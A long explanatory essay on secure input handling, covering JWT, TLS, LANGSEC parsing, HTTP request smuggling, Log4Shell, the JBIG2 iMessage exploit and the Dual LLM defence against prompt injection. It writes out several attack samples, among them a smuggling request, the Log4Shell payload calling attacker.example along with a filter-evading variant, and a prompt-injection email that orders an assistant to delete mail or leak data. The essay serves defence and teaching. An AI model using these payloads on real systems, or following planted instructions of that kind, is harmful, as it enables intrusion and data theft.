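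Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, applied Hardy's term "confused deputy" to an email assistant that deletes its owner's messages because one of them contains an instruction to do so. A blog post by the security vendor Semgrep, *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), recommends capabilities as the remedy for agents in general. That recommendation is too broad, because Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, prove that capabilities prevent only some of these attacks. By their definition, a program is safe if, for every location the attacker wants to change, the attacker either has no influence on what ends up there or could have written the same value himself.

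Capabilities prevent the attack on the compiler because the attacker has to supply the target. They don't help if the deputy already holds a reference to the target and the attacker influences what the deputy writes there. In one of Rajani and colleagues' examples, the deputy copies a value from a place the attacker controls into a protected location. In another, it writes one of two fixed numbers, depending on a true-or-false value the attacker sets.

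The refund assistant is open to this kind of influence, since Ada's email affects whether the service pays and how much, as the shop intends. Rajani and colleagues allow for intended influence by letting the programmer mark parts of a program as "endorsed", which exempts them from the definition. Their example is the compiler's bill, which a customer's program has to be able to affect. A designer should therefore be able to list every decision that untrusted text is meant to influence. For the refund assistant, these are whether to pay, for which order, for which reason and what share to refund.

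Rajani and colleagues also give a method that stops all the attacks in their small model language. It labels each value with the least trusted source that affected it, and keeps values with a low-trust label out of protected locations. The labels must follow every branch in the program as well as every copied value, which slows the program.

### Rules about order

Some messages are dangerous only at the wrong moment. A bank should take a payment only after it has authorised it. Session types, which the computer scientist Kohei Honda introduced in the early 1990s, describe a whole conversation as a type, much as "whole number" describes a value. In a simplified notation, `!` means send, `?` means receive and a full stop means "then". The shop's side of a card payment looks like this:

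`!Authorise . ?{ Approved: !Pay . ?Receipt . end | Refused: end }`

The shop sends a request with the card and the amount, then waits. If the bank approves, the shop sends Pay and receives a receipt. If the bank refuses, the conversation ends. The bank's type is the same with every `!` and `?` swapped, so each side is ready to receive what the other sends.

A compiler that supports session types tracks which messages the protocol still permits at each point in the shop's program. At the start only Authorise is permitted, so a program that opens with Pay doesn't compile. After a refusal, the program can't send anything more. Pay appears only once in the protocol, so the program can't charge the card twice in one conversation. The program also mustn't keep a copy of the channel from an earlier point, because that copy would still allow a Pay. Each step therefore uses up the channel and returns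 a new one.

The compiler checks only the programs it compiles, and the bank can't know how a stranger wrote his. The bank therefore also has to track the conversation as it happens:

| State at the bank | Message the shop may send | What happens next |
|---|---|---|
| New | Authorise | The bank starts to decide |
| Deciding | None | The bank approves, or refuses and closes |
| Approved | Pay | The bank takes the money, sends a receipt and closes |
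| Closed | None | Nothing |

The Pay message carries no amount, because a shop could otherwise get approval for £10 and then charge £1,000. The bank uses the amount it approved. Basic session types don't represent time, so the designer must also decide how long an approval lasts.

TLS, the protocol that encrypts most web traffic, has a similar rule. Rescorla's *The Transport Layer Security (TLS) Protocol Version 1.3* forbids either side to send application data before its own Finished message, which contains a keyed checksum of the whole opening exchange. One exception lets a returning client send data immediately, which saves a round trip but gives up some protection. Rescorla also warns that once the server has sent its own Finished message, it can send data to a client that has not yet authenticated itself. To prevent this, a designer has to make the server wait for the client's Finished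 message too.

### Taking dangerous options out of a protocol

JSON Web Tokens show what can happen when a dangerous option stays in the permitted set. A server gives a user a token, which is a signed note with content such as "logged in as admin", and checks it when the user presents it again. The token's header has an "alg" field that names the signature algorithm. A 2015 review on chosenplaintext.ca pointed out that this is circular. The server must read the header to determine how to check the token, but until it has checked the token, it can't rule out that an attacker wrote the header.

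The field could be set to "none" for tokens that some other mechanism had already protected, and the standard required every library to support this value. Some libraries treated a token marked "none" as correctly signed, so anyone could write "logged in as admin" in a token and leave the signature empty.

Another attack relies on confusing two kinds of key. With RSA, a server signs with a private key and can publish a second key that anyone may use to check the signature. With HMAC, the same secret key is used for both signing and checking. An attacker signs a token with HMAC, using the server's public RSA key as the secret, and names HMAC in the token's header. A careless library takes the algorithm from the header and checks the token with HMAC and the same public key, so the signature matches.

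Some libraries responded to the "none" attack by filtering out a list of forbidden algorithm names. Attackers got past the filter by writing "noNE", according to *JSON Web Token Best Current Practices* (Sheffer, Hardt and Jones, 2026), a draft of official guidance. The filter didn't recognise that spelling, but the code that chose the algorithm ignored capitalisation. The draft recommends a list of permitted algorithms instead, since nobody can anticipate every variant spelling.

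Eleven years after the review, the option is still in the standard. In *JOSE*, a draft named after the family of standards that covers these tokens, Madden (2026) proposes to deprecate it. He cites a tally of 17 public reports of software that accepted "none" by mistake. Of the ten he lists with official identifiers, three are rated "critical". The draft deprecates the option rather than banning it so that existing systems can keep using unsigned tokens, for example over a connection that TLS already protects.

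PASETO, a rival token format from the security company Paragon Initiative Enterprises, has no algorithm field. Its only options are a version and a purpose, which is either "local" (encrypted with a shared key) or "public" (signed with a private key) (Paragon Initiative Enterprises, 2019). According to the draft specification, IETF's *PASETO* (2022), versions are fixed to prevent unsafe configurations. A public token in version 4, for example, always uses the signature algorithm Ed25519.

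An attacker can change the version or purpose written in a PASETO token. But when Paragon Initiative Enterprises announced versions 3 and 4, it specified that each key works with only one version and one purpose, so a library that follows this rule won't use a public signing key as a shared secret. The company is describing its own product, and a sound design doesn't prove that the libraries implementing it have fewer bugs.

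TLS 1.3, first specified by Rescorla (2018), removed many of the protocol's options. Older versions let a client encrypt a session's secret with the server's long-term RSA key, so anyone who recorded the traffic and later stole that key could read it. Every public-key method in version 1.3 protects past sessions against such a theft. The new version also dropped custom Diffie-Hellman groups, which let one side choose weak numbers for agreeing on a key. Packt's textbook chapter *Major differences between TLS versions 1.3 and 1.2* also lists the RC4 cipher and the insecure CBC mode as removed. All the remaining ciphers both encrypt messages and detect tampering.

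Compression was also removed, although it looks harmless. Sheffer and colleagues explain in their guidance on tokens that repetitive data compresses to a shorter length, so an attacker who can insert text next to a secret can try guesses and watch the length of the message. When a guess matches part of the secret, the message gets shorter, and encryption doesn't hide the change.

Removing an option from a new version does little good if both sides can still fall back to an old version. Rescorla's current text therefore forbids negotiating TLS 1.0 or 1.1. It still allows TLS 1.2, along with some options that version 1.3 dropped.

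### When a field has to carry code

Some fields can't be limited to a short list of choices. A web page may need to insert formatted text, which can contain scripts. In *If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile*, Wang, Bangert and Kern describe a search page that copies the visitor's search term from the web address into the page. An attacker sends someone a link whose search term contains a script, and the browser runs it with the page's permissions. This form of cross-site scripting happens entirely in the browser, through the DOM, the browser's live model of the page.

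The commands that insert such text into a page accept any string. Wang and colleagues at Google replaced them with versions that accept only values of special types, such as a type for safe HTML. Six such types cover the five kinds of dangerous command they found. A program can turn a string into safe HTML only by using one of a few approved functions, which escape or check the string first. The compiler rejects any program that passes an ordinary string to one of the new versions, much as a prepared statement keeps a password from being read as part of a command. Trusted Types, a web standard that grew out of this work, moves the check into the browser.

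Google first tested the method on a single product. People reported 10 of these flaws in the year before the team adopted it, 2 during the changeover year and 1 in the year after. If reports had kept arriving at random at the old rate, a year with one or none would occur about once in 2,000 years, so luck is an unlikely explanation. But there was no comparison group, and the team also spent a year cleaning up its code. Across the company, the share of these flaws among serious outside reports fell steadily from 2018, and a growing proportion of them came from old code that didn't use the new types. The shift toward old code is better evidence for the method, because a general improvement in security would probably have helped old code too.

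Few programmers needed anything the types couldn't express. By the end of 2020, Google had more than a million JavaScript files, and fewer than 1% had an exemption from any of the checks. During five months of the early rollout, the security team received fewer than eight exemption requests a week, while programmers submitted roughly 10,000 changes a week involving JavaScript. Wang and colleagues concede that a programmer can defeat the compiler by declaring that a value has a different type, and they rely on code review to catch this. The method therefore protects more against carelessness than against deliberate misuse by colleagues.

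Security Boulevard's *Google fights DOM XSS with Trusted Types* (2021) reports that Google turned on Trusted Types in the browser for 130 services and found no DOM XSS flaws in them afterwards. This is Google's own figure, and it depends on how hard people looked. Google also has a single code repository and mandatory code review, which make the change much easier. PortSwigger's *Internal deployment has nullified elusive, complex threat since 2019* reports that Mozilla engineers worried Trusted Types would be too complex for most smaller websites. *Trust me if you can*, a study that interviewed 13 web developers and set them a coding task, also identifies key weaknesses in the design.

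web.dev's *Prevent DOM-based cross-site scripting vulnerabilities with Trusted Types* explains that, with Trusted Types switched on, only approved functions, called policies, can introduce such vulnerabilities. A site's developers can then focus their review on a few functions. When developers can't rewrite outside code that the site loads, the guide suggests a default policy, which runs every ordinary string through a program that strips out dangerous markup. This brings back filtering, but with only one filter to maintain.

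### The case for protocols that can change

An algorithm that looks safe today may later be broken, as happened to RC4, once among the most widely used ciphers on the web. If TLS had supported only RC4, its users would have been stuck with a broken cipher until both ends of every connection were updated. When a protocol supports several algorithms, an operator can quickly switch off the broken one, and both sides can use another they already have.

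Sheffer and colleagues accept this argument. Their draft describes the attacks on the "alg" field but still requires applications to support "cryptographic agility", the ability to change algorithms, because the set of safe algorithms changes over time. TLS 1.3 still lets the two sides choose, though from a shorter list. The current specification widened its wording on key exchange to cover the newer family of methods used in most designs meant to resist quantum computers, without changing the version number.

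Defenders of fixed versions point out that a new algorithm needs new code in any protocol, so a quick switch works only if both sides have already installed the replacement. Until it is needed, the replacement is one more option that may contain a flaw. Somebody also has to check that every combination of options is safe, and four key exchanges, five ciphers and three hash functions make 60 combinations.

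But fixed versions don't remove the choice entirely, because receivers have to accept both the old and the new version while users switch. PASETO had four versions when Paragon Initiative Enterprises agreed with a critic that supporting more than two modes in parallel was an unnecessary risk. The company planned to retire the two oldest in January 2022.

Much of the conflict disappears if the operator, rather than the message, chooses the algorithm. The review on chosenplaintext.ca proposed dropping the "alg" field and relying on a key identifier. The server looks up the key, and the key's record specifies the one algorithm to use with it, so an attacker can't choose a different one. If that algorithm is broken, the operator issues a new key for a better one and withdraws the old key, without changing the token format.

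This works when the server already knows whose keys to expect. When a browser visits a website for the first time, the two have to negotiate which options to use. TLS protects the negotiation by including it in the checksum of the Finished message. If an attacker removes the strong options from the browser's list in transit, the checksums won't match and the connection fails.

The shop with the refund assistant will face the same problem on a small scale. If the manufacturer recalls Ada's kettle, none of the five reasons fits. The developers have to add a sixth to both the assistant and the payment service, which raises the count to 49 messages. The service may have to accept both the old and new formats for a few days. An "other" option with a text box would be quicker to add, and the developers would never have to extend the list again, but the box would carry the same risk as the help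 desk's "notes" field.

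## Enforcing the permitted set and keeping it from growing

A developer who adds an "other" box changes the written format, so a colleague can at least object. But the permitted set can also grow while the written format stays the same, because the payment service acts on any message its code accepts. If the specification lists 41 messages but the code also accepts a refund that names two slots, that refund is part of the permitted set even though nobody has worked out what it does.

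Language-theoretic security is largely an attempt to close this gap. Its first rule, according to the slogans on the LANGSEC website, is to recognise the whole input before processing any of it. Programs often scatter their checks among the code that processes the input instead, which the website calls a "shotgun parser".

### Checking the whole message before acting on it

A payment service written as a shotgun parser might read the slot number, look up the order and mark it as refunded before reading the share. If the share is "triple", the service stops with an error, and the order is marked as refunded even though Ada hasn't received her money. A recogniser would have checked the whole message against the format and rejected it before the service touched the order. When a message is valid, the recogniser should pass on typed values, such as slot 3 and "half", and discard the original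 text so that later code can't interpret it differently.

In *Best Practices for Secure Data Intake, Data Modeling, and Data Design*, Bratus draws on a DARPA research programme about safe document formats. He warns that when a program mixes checking with other work, it is often unclear which assumptions the code has already checked. Often, one piece of code checks the size and type of each field, and the application later checks how the fields relate to each other. Bratus criticises this approach because by then the application is already acting on the data.

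*What We Have Here Is Failure to Validate* (Ali, Anantharaman and colleagues, 2021) reviews ten flaws that came to light in the summer of 2020. Several were in Treck's network software, which runs in hundreds of millions of devices. In one of the Treck flaws, the code reserved memory according to the length stated in an incoming record, then copied in a name built from the record's contents. An attacker could state a short length and supply a long name, which overwrote whatever lay next to the reserved memory. A check that compared the stated length with the name would have rejected the record.

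A recogniser also has to check the message to its end. Sassaman and colleagues discuss a forgery of RSA signatures that Daniel Bleichenbacher presented in 2006. To check a signature, the receiver raises it to a public power, which for some keys is 3. The result should fill the whole block with fixed padding followed by a fingerprint of the signed document. Some libraries read the padding and the fingerprint but ignored any digits after them.

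In a small decimal version, let 1234 stand for the padding and the fingerprint, and suppose the library ignores the next nine digits. The cube of 10,727 is 1,234,340,110,583, which begins with 1234, so the library accepts 10,727 as a signature. Anyone can find this number by taking the cube root of 1,234,000,000,000 on a calculator and rounding up. If the library also checked the last nine digits, rounding up would no longer work and the forger would need the private key.

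Many programs deliberately accept malformed messages. An old rule of internet engineering advises programmers to be liberal in what they accept, so that imperfect programs can work together. But each program accepts different mistakes, so an attacker can look for one that a security check misses and the receiver accepts. Ali and colleagues describe such a flaw in a communications module made by Thales. The module refused requests for certain files, but its check worked only for paths with single slashes. If an attacker typed a double slash, the check let the request through, and the module ignored the extra slash and opened the file.

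Bratus recommends treating every deviation from the specification as fatal. He also advises against repairing bad input, since a repair can create the thing it was meant to remove. For example, a program that deletes `<script>` from its input will turn `<scr<script>ipt>` into `<script>`. Strictness is easiest to adopt in a new format, because a browser that began rejecting every malformed web page would be unable to show much of the web.

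### Keeping the grammar simple enough to check

Theorists classify formats by how powerful a machine must be to recognise them. A format's class affects what a designer can find out about its parser before using it.

| Type of grammar | Example of a permitted set | What a recogniser needs | Can software always tell whether two grammars permit the same messages? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Regular | Any number of digits | A fixed amount of memory | Yes |
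| Deterministic context-free | Balanced brackets, such as `(()())` | A stack, and no guessing | Yes |
| General context-free | Words that read the same backwards, such as "level" | A stack, and sometimes guessing | No |
| Context-sensitive | A length followed by that many letters, such as `5:tulip` | Memory in proportion to the message | No |
| Unrestricted | Programs that eventually finish | No recogniser can always answer | No |

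A stack is a pile of notes, and a program can read only the top one. To check that brackets match, the program adds a note for each opening bracket and removes one for each closing bracket, and the pile should be empty at the end. To check that "level" reads the same backwards, it could put the first half of the word on the stack and compare it with the second half, but it has to guess where the middle is.

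Several research tools for stopping SQL injection approximated SQL with a regular grammar, which made them too weak in the way Hansen and Patterson warned about. The developers of one tool argued that the nested patterns a regular grammar leaves out didn't occur in practice, but Sassaman and colleagues found four places in PostgreSQL's grammar that use them.

A recogniser for an unrestricted grammar may run for ever on some messages, so an attacker can stop the service by sending one. The other types of grammar are all decidable, meaning that some recogniser always gives an answer. But a message usually passes through more than one parser, and the designer also needs to know whether they all accept the same set. For general context-free grammars, no program can always work this out. The proof shows that such a program would also solve Turing's problem of telling whether a program ever finishes:

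1. Take any program P that needs no input. Write out its run as one long text, with a snapshot of its memory after every step. If P finishes, this text is its complete record. If P never finishes, it has no complete record.
2. Write a grammar G that permits every text except a complete record of P. A context-free grammar can do this because a text needs only one mistake to qualify. A parser can guess where the mistake is, then use its stack to compare two neighbouring snapshots.
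3. Write a second grammar H that permits every text.
4. If P never finishes, G and H permit the same texts. If P does finish, G leaves one out. A program that could always compare two context-free grammars could therefore tell whether P finishes.

Step 2 relies on guessing. A deterministic grammar never requires its parser to guess, and computer scientist Géraud Sénizergues proved in 1997 that software can always compare two such grammars. LANGSEC's advice to use "only regular and context-free protocols" should therefore be narrowed slightly, to regular and deterministic context-free protocols. Sassaman and colleagues wrongly treat every unambiguous grammar as deterministic. Palindromes, for example, have an unambiguous grammar, but their parser has to guess where the middle is.

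When a format changes, a reviewer needs to know whether the new version permits any message that the old one didn't. A program can't always determine this, even when both versions have deterministic grammars. If both grammars are regular, standard algorithms can always determine it and can print an example of a new message if there is one. This is a good reason to keep a format regular. The refund format is regular because it has only 41 messages.

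The type of grammar is only a rough guide to risk. Most network protocols use length fields, which Sassaman and colleagues count as context-sensitive. But if the length can't exceed, for example, 255, the format has a finite number of cases and is therefore regular. A length field is easy to check, but programmers can forget to check it.

### Parser differentials and HTTP request smuggling

Two parsers can accept the same message but interpret it differently. Sassaman and colleagues give an example from the certificates that websites use to prove their identity. An attacker who owned badguy.com could request a certificate for `www.paypal.com\x00.badguy.com`, where `\x00` is a byte with the value zero. The certificate authority would read the whole name, see that it belonged to badguy.com and sign the certificate. Some browsers treated the zero byte as the end of the name, so they accepted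 the certificate as PayPal's.

HTTP request smuggling exploits a similar disagreement about where a message ends. Many websites put a proxy in front of their main server, and the proxy sends requests from many visitors down a single connection, so the server has to work out where each request ends. HTTP/1.1 has two ways to mark the end. A Content-Length header gives the number of bytes in the body. With chunked encoding, the body arrives in pieces, each preceded by its length, and a piece of length 0 ends it.

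Suppose an attacker sends the shop this request, which uses both:

```
POST /search HTTP/1.1
Host: shop.example
Content-Length: 37
Transfer-Encoding: chunked

0

POST /close-account HTTP/1.1
X:
```

The proxy uses Content-Length, so it counts 37 bytes after the first blank line, up to and including `X:`, and forwards everything as one search request. The server uses chunked encoding, so it reads the 0 as the end of the search request and keeps the remaining 32 bytes as the start of another request.

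Ada now opens her basket, and her browser sends `GET /basket HTTP/1.1`, followed by the cookie that shows she is logged in. The server adds this to the end of the bytes it kept. It reads `X:GET /basket HTTP/1.1` as a meaningless header, finds Ada's cookie on a later line and closes her account, unless the page for closing accounts requires further proof. A filter on the proxy that blocked outside requests to close accounts wouldn't have helped, because the proxy read only a search request.

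The current HTTP/1.1 standard gives chunked encoding priority over Content-Length and allows servers to reject requests that use both. Attackers get around this by putting a small error in the Transfer-Encoding header, such as a space before the colon. If the proxy ignores the malformed header and the server accepts it, they again differ on where the request ends. Either program might be safe when paired with another copy of itself, so testing them separately can miss the problem.

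Apple had the same problem within its own software. Ali and colleagues report that the iPhone's operating system used at least four parsers for XML, a common text format, and that they handled malformed comment markers differently. An app's permissions are listed in XML, so an attacker could add permissions that one parser skipped as a comment and another read as real, giving the app powers Apple had never approved.

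One remedy is to generate every parser from the same grammar. Another is to let only one component parse the sender's bytes. The shop's proxy could read each request, reject any it can't fully account for, and replace each of the others with a new request that has a single Content-Length header. The server would then never receive the attacker's spacing or second length. The new request should be in canonical form, where each meaning has exactly one permitted encoding. In Ada's orders, slot 1 would always be written as "1", never "01" or "+1".

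Agreement about the bytes isn't always enough. In the Shadow attack on PDF files, which Ali and colleagues also describe, an attacker prepares a contract with hidden content and gets someone to sign it. He then adds an update that reveals the content, and the viewer still shows the signature as valid. A viewer that rejected every document changed after signing would also reject forms that people need to fill in after somebody has approved them.

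### Rebuilding messages at a gateway

Writing a fresh message still requires a program that can read the old one. For a complex format such as PDF, this program will be complex too, and the gateway vendor Everfox points out that an attacker might take control of it through a flaw in how it handles unusual data. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) addressed this in *Pattern: Safely Importing Data* by splitting the work between two components. One transforms the data into a simpler format, and the other, which an attacker can't reach directly, verifies the result.

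Suppose the shop wants customers to send photographs of damaged goods. A gateway could handle Ada's picture of her lamp in four steps:

1. The transformer decodes the photograph and writes it out as plain pixels. The new file starts with the width and height, in two bytes each, followed by three bytes of colour for each pixel.
2. A one-way link carries the file to the verifier.
3. The verifier checks that the width and height are each between 1 and 2,000 and that the file has exactly 4 + 3 × width × height bytes. For a picture 1,000 pixels wide and 800 high, that is 2,400,004 bytes.
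4. A program inside the shop's network turns the pixels back into an ordinary image file.

Every possible byte is a valid colour value, so any file that passes is a picture. The gateway doesn't rely on the transformer. An attacker who takes complete control of the transformer can send any picture, including a forged one, but would have to exploit a flaw in a check only a few lines long to get anything else through.

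Glasswall's *Boost your Hardsec deployments with turbocharged, zero-trust CDR file protection* describes a commercial version in which software transforms the files and a field-programmable gate array verifies them. The manufacturer configures this chip's circuits for one task, so an attacker has much less software to hijack. Deep Secure's *Government Safely Uploading Data* (2020) reports that a public authority also followed the NCSC's pattern to let citizens upload documents, and calls the uploaded files "100% malware‑free". That is a seller's claim, and the design supports a narrower one, that the files contain only what the simple format can express.

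Rebuilding a photograph as plain pixels also usually makes the file several times larger and removes the stored location and date. A rebuilt spreadsheet may lose its formulas, and a signed document loses its signature, because the signature covers bytes that no longer exist. This matters little for a photograph of a lamp, but a lawyer who needs the signed original can't use the rebuilt copy.

Government rules differ in how much they require. The security manual from New Zealand's signals intelligence agency, the GCSB, requires validation of all data passing through a content filter on systems classified Confidential or above, and recommends it on other systems. In Britain, Digital Watch's *NCSC publishes new cross-domain architecture guidance* reports that the NCSC is retiring its original import and export patterns and will gradually replace them. The new guidance, NCSC's *Cross domain approach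 and architecture* (2026), says that no single appliance between two networks can eliminate the risk, and asks designers to plan the whole flow of data. It is meant for organisations that expect targeted attacks through previously unknown flaws. A small shop would probably do better to ask customers for fewer types of file.

#### One-way links

The link in step 2 can be a hardware device called a data diode. A typical one is an optical fibre with a light source at one end and a sensor at the other. The receiving side has no light source, so it can't send anything back, even if an attacker has fully corrupted its software.

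Most network protocols need replies. A computer sending a file over TCP, for example, waits for confirmation that each part has arrived. The equipment therefore has to end the ordinary protocol on the sending side, pass the bare data across and start a new connection on the other side. This also removes attacks hidden in the protocol's headers, because the receiving side writes its own. The sending side gets no confirmation that the data arrived, so it has to send extra copies or codes that let the receiver repair errors.

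The diode's direction depends on what the owner wants to protect. A power station can send its readings out through a diode so that no one can send commands back in. Waterfall Security's *How to Apply the NCSC/CISA 2026 Guidance* says that recent official advice for industrial sites heavily emphasises this "push-only" arrangement, though Waterfall sells the hardware for it. An intelligence agency can import documents through a diode facing the other way, so that a malicious document can't send secrets back along the same link. Australian Signals Directorate (2019) lists diodes and content filters among the common parts of such gateways.

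A diode restricts the direction of a message but not its contents, so a malicious document still gets in. If the agency also exports documents, the two links form a loop, and an attacker might send instructions in through one and receive secrets through the other. Everfox's *Implementing the UK National Cyber Security Centre Principles for Cross Domain Solutions* (2024) describes a design that keeps the two flows separate, each with its own one-way hardware. Each flow still needs its own verifier.

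### Parsers that come with a proof

The verifier at the shop's gateway is short enough for a person to check by reading it, but most parsers are much longer. *EverParse* (Ramananandro, Delignat-Lavaud and colleagues, 2019) presents a tool that generates a parser from a description of a message format, along with a computer-checked proof about the parser. The tool works on binary formats in which each field has a tag and a length, like those in many network protocols.

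*EverParse* proves three properties of its parser. The parser is safe, so no message can make it write outside its memory the way the record with the false length did to Treck's software. It is correct, so it recovers the original values from a message that another program wrote. It is also "non-malleable", meaning each message has only one encoding, so an attacker can't alter the bytes of a signed message while keeping its meaning. The shop's proxy needs this canonical form, and the proof shows that the parser enforces it.

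Proofs of this kind no longer require slow code. Ramananandro and colleagues put their parsers into existing C programs and found them significantly faster than earlier handwritten libraries. The abstract of a later talk, also called *EverParse*, reports that Microsoft uses the tool in Hyper-V, the software that runs virtual machines in its Azure cloud. Every network packet that passes through Azure is parsed first by generated code, which rejects malformed packets. In 2022 the tool's developers reported that generated parsers had replaced handwritten ones for nearly 100 types of message.

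Writing the description takes most of the effort. For an old format, somebody has to reconstruct the rules from standards documents and existing programs, which may contradict each other. Some tools are also harder to install than others. In Bratus's comparison of several tools from DARPA's programme, Hammer needs little more than an ordinary C compiler, while DaeDaLus and Parsley give stronger guarantees but require less common software. A designer who controls both ends of the channel can save effort by adopting a ready-made format that comes with its own parser generator.

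Ali and colleagues note that few developers had adopted language-theoretic methods by 2021, and that nobody had studied how easy the tools were to use. They expected the extra running time to be small in large programs. Microsoft's experience supports this, but Microsoft, unlike most companies, can afford specialists in formal proof.

Proving a parser correct also doesn't show that the receiver handles every valid message properly. In June 2020, people discovered a photograph that made some Android phones restart endlessly when set as wallpaper. The file was valid, but one of its pixels caused an overflow when the phone calculated its brightness. The Windows software that looks up internet addresses had a similar flaw. The code stored the length of a record in a 16-bit number, which can't exceed 65,535, but an attacker could use compression to build a longer valid record. A parser proved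 correct against the standard would have accepted both the photograph and the record. Ali and colleagues recommend either repairing the code or narrowing the permitted set to the messages it can handle. Rejecting records over 65,535 bytes would have closed the Windows flaw, with little disruption if nobody needed such records.

### When a data format contains a language

Some formats that seem to hold only data also hold commands. Poll, in *Secure input handling*, warns that a text parameter can hide a very powerful language, because the same string may be a name in one program and a command in another. A spreadsheet cell can be a formula, and a PDF can contain JavaScript. The trade magazine Intersec (2018) describes a PNG image that is harmless in an image viewer but that a spreadsheet program can open as a table, including formulas that run an attacker's code.

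#### The image that contained a computer

In 2021, the Israeli spyware company NSO Group was breaking into iPhones by sending iMessages, and the owners didn't have to touch anything. Ian Beer and Samuel Groß of Project Zero, Google's team for finding unknown security flaws, published an analysis of the attack that December.

The messages contained files with names ending in ".gif", the usual ending for short animations. Apple wanted these animations to repeat endlessly, so iMessage copied each one to change its repeat setting. The copying code used a general image library that ignores the file's name and works out the format from its contents. iMessage therefore accepted more than twenty formats, including PDF, through a channel that seemed to accept only GIF.

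The attacker's files were PDFs with an image in JBIG2, an old format for compressing black-and-white scans. JBIG2 saves space by storing the shape of a letter once and listing where it appears. If a later copy looks slightly different, the file can correct the shape by combining it with a second one, pixel by pixel. The permitted operations include AND, which gives 1 if both pixels are 1, and XOR, which gives 1 if exactly one of them is.

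These are the basic operations of a computer. To add two binary digits, XOR gives the digit to write down and AND gives the digit to carry. So for 1 + 1, XOR gives 0 and AND gives 1, which together make binary 10, or two.

In a correct decoder, this arithmetic can affect only the picture. But Apple's decoder stored the total number of shapes in a 32-bit number, and the attacker made the total so large that it wrapped around to a small one. The decoder therefore reserved too little memory and wrote past the end of it. The attacker used those writes to change the recorded size of the picture, so that the decoder treated other parts of the phone's memory as pixels. The attacker then used more than 70,000 drawing commands to build a small computer out of these operations, with a 64-bit adder, that ran the next stage of the attack.

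The attack needed the bug as well as the drawing commands. A recogniser could have stopped it by checking the total number of shapes or by accepting only real GIF files. Apple fixed the bug in September 2021. It later restricted the formats that this part of iMessage could open and moved GIF handling into an isolated process.

#### A feature that turned log entries into commands

Log4j is a library that Java programs use to keep logs. A log entry may contain text from strangers, such as the name someone typed into a login form. This is normally safe because the program only stores the text, as with a password in a prepared statement.

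In 2013, Log4j's developers accepted a contributor's proposal to let expressions starting with `${jndi:` fetch values from a directory server, which is convenient in configuration files. But Log4j also evaluated such expressions in the text of log entries. If an attacker typed `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}` as a user name and the application logged it, Log4j contacted the attacker's server, and on many systems it could load and run code from there.

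The flaw became public in December 2021 under the name Log4Shell, more than eight years after Log4j added the feature. Programmers who used Log4j hadn't changed their own formats. A user name was still a string, but a library upgrade had given some strings a new meaning.

Some companies tried to filter out requests containing `${jndi:`. Attackers then wrote `${${lower:j}ndi:`, which Log4j converts into the forbidden text by evaluating `${lower:j}` as `j`. The developers' first fix was also incomplete. In the next version, they stopped Log4j from evaluating any expressions in log entries and turned the directory feature off by default. Bratus cites Log4Shell as proof that developers must validate supposedly passive descriptive data as thoroughly as any other data, since some program will eventually act on it.

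### Reviewing changes

The difference between the old and new permitted sets is the most useful thing for a reviewer to examine. When the shop adds "recalled" as a sixth reason for a refund, the difference is 8 messages (4 slots × 2 shares), few enough to read in full. If the format is regular but too large to list, software can compute the difference and print samples from it. Some changes need closer attention because they add far more messages than their authors intend.

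When someone proposes a new free-text field, the reviewer should ask which programs will read it, including the log, the monthly spreadsheet and any language model that summarises complaints. Any fact that one of these programs needs should go in a typed field instead.

*Extension points* include plug-ins, fields reserved for future use and fields that tell the receiver which format to expect. A library can add one in an upgrade, as Log4j did, so the reviewer should treat an upgrade as a possible change to the format. New features should be off by default. The recogniser should reject unknown fields, because a receiver that ignores them today may begin to act on them after an upgrade.

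Developers should leave debugging commands out of the version they release, since a setting that disables them is easy to change. In 1988, the first major internet worm spread partly through a debugging command in Sendmail, a widely used mail program. The command let a stranger address a message to a program instead of a person, and the receiving computer ran that program. Developers can check the finished product by sending it each debugging command and confirming that it rejects them all.

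*Version fallback.* HTTP/2 gives each piece of a request a length in a fixed position, which removes the ambiguity in the smuggling example. But many proxies translate HTTP/2 requests into HTTP/1.1 for the server behind them, and in 2021 the security researcher James Kettle showed that the translation brings the attack back. The reviewer needs a list of the versions each component accepts and a date for removing each old one. After that date, a test should send a message in the removed version and check that it is rejected.

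The team should also test all the parsers on the path against each other, even when a change seems to affect only one of them. Sassaman and colleagues' method is to give two parsers the same input and compare the structures they produce. For the refund service, the test could run as follows:

1. List every component that reads any part of the message, including proxies and logging tools.
2. Generate all 49 valid messages. Then make damaged copies, with repeated fields, extra spaces, different capitals, wrong lengths, unusual character encodings and additional bytes at the end.
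3. Send the same bytes to every component and record whether it accepts them and which values it reads.
4. Treat any disagreement as a fault, even if nobody can yet see how to exploit it.
5. Add each damaged message that caused a disagreement to a permanent set of tests.

Bratus lists a tool for this, the Format Analysis Workbench, which runs any number of parsers on the same file and helps compare their output. He also warns against trusting a parser because of testing alone. The refund team can test all 49 valid messages, but it can't test every damaged one because there is no limit to their number. The team should repeat the whole test when any component changes, including bought ones, because a supplier's update can make parsers disagree even when the shop's own code stays the same.

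## Letting a language model send only typed answers and requests

The model that reads Ada's emails can only choose one of the shop's 49 messages. That is enough for refunds, but people also want assistants that can search their files, send email and edit code, often acting on text from strangers. If one model reads that text and can do all of these things, a stranger can plant an instruction that makes the model misuse any of those abilities. Dividing the work between two models prevents this, as long as the stranger's text never passes from one to the other.

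### The Dual LLM pattern

Willison proposed such a division in 2023 and called it the Dual LLM pattern (LLM stands for large language model). A privileged model takes the user's requests and chooses actions, but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model, like the one at the help desk, reads that text instead. An ordinary program, the controller, carries out the actions and passes material between them. Suppose a user asks for a summary of her latest email:

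1. The privileged model asks the controller to fetch the email and call it `$VAR1`.
2. The controller fetches it and reports only that `$VAR1` now exists.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`.
4. The controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`.
5. The privileged model asks the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

The privileged model can pass on the opaque variables `$VAR1` and `$VAR2` by name but cannot read their contents. If the email contains an instruction to delete every message in the inbox, the quarantined model may well try to follow it, but it has no tool for deleting anything.

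The user still reads the summary, which the email's author may have influenced. Willison imagines a summary with instructions to paste some scrambled letters into a website to see a funny picture of a monkey, when the letters are the user's encoded private data. Even displaying an image can leak data if the image's web address contains it, so he would allow only approved addresses. He called his own proposal "pretty bad", partly because one programming mistake that lets text through to the privileged model undoes the protection.

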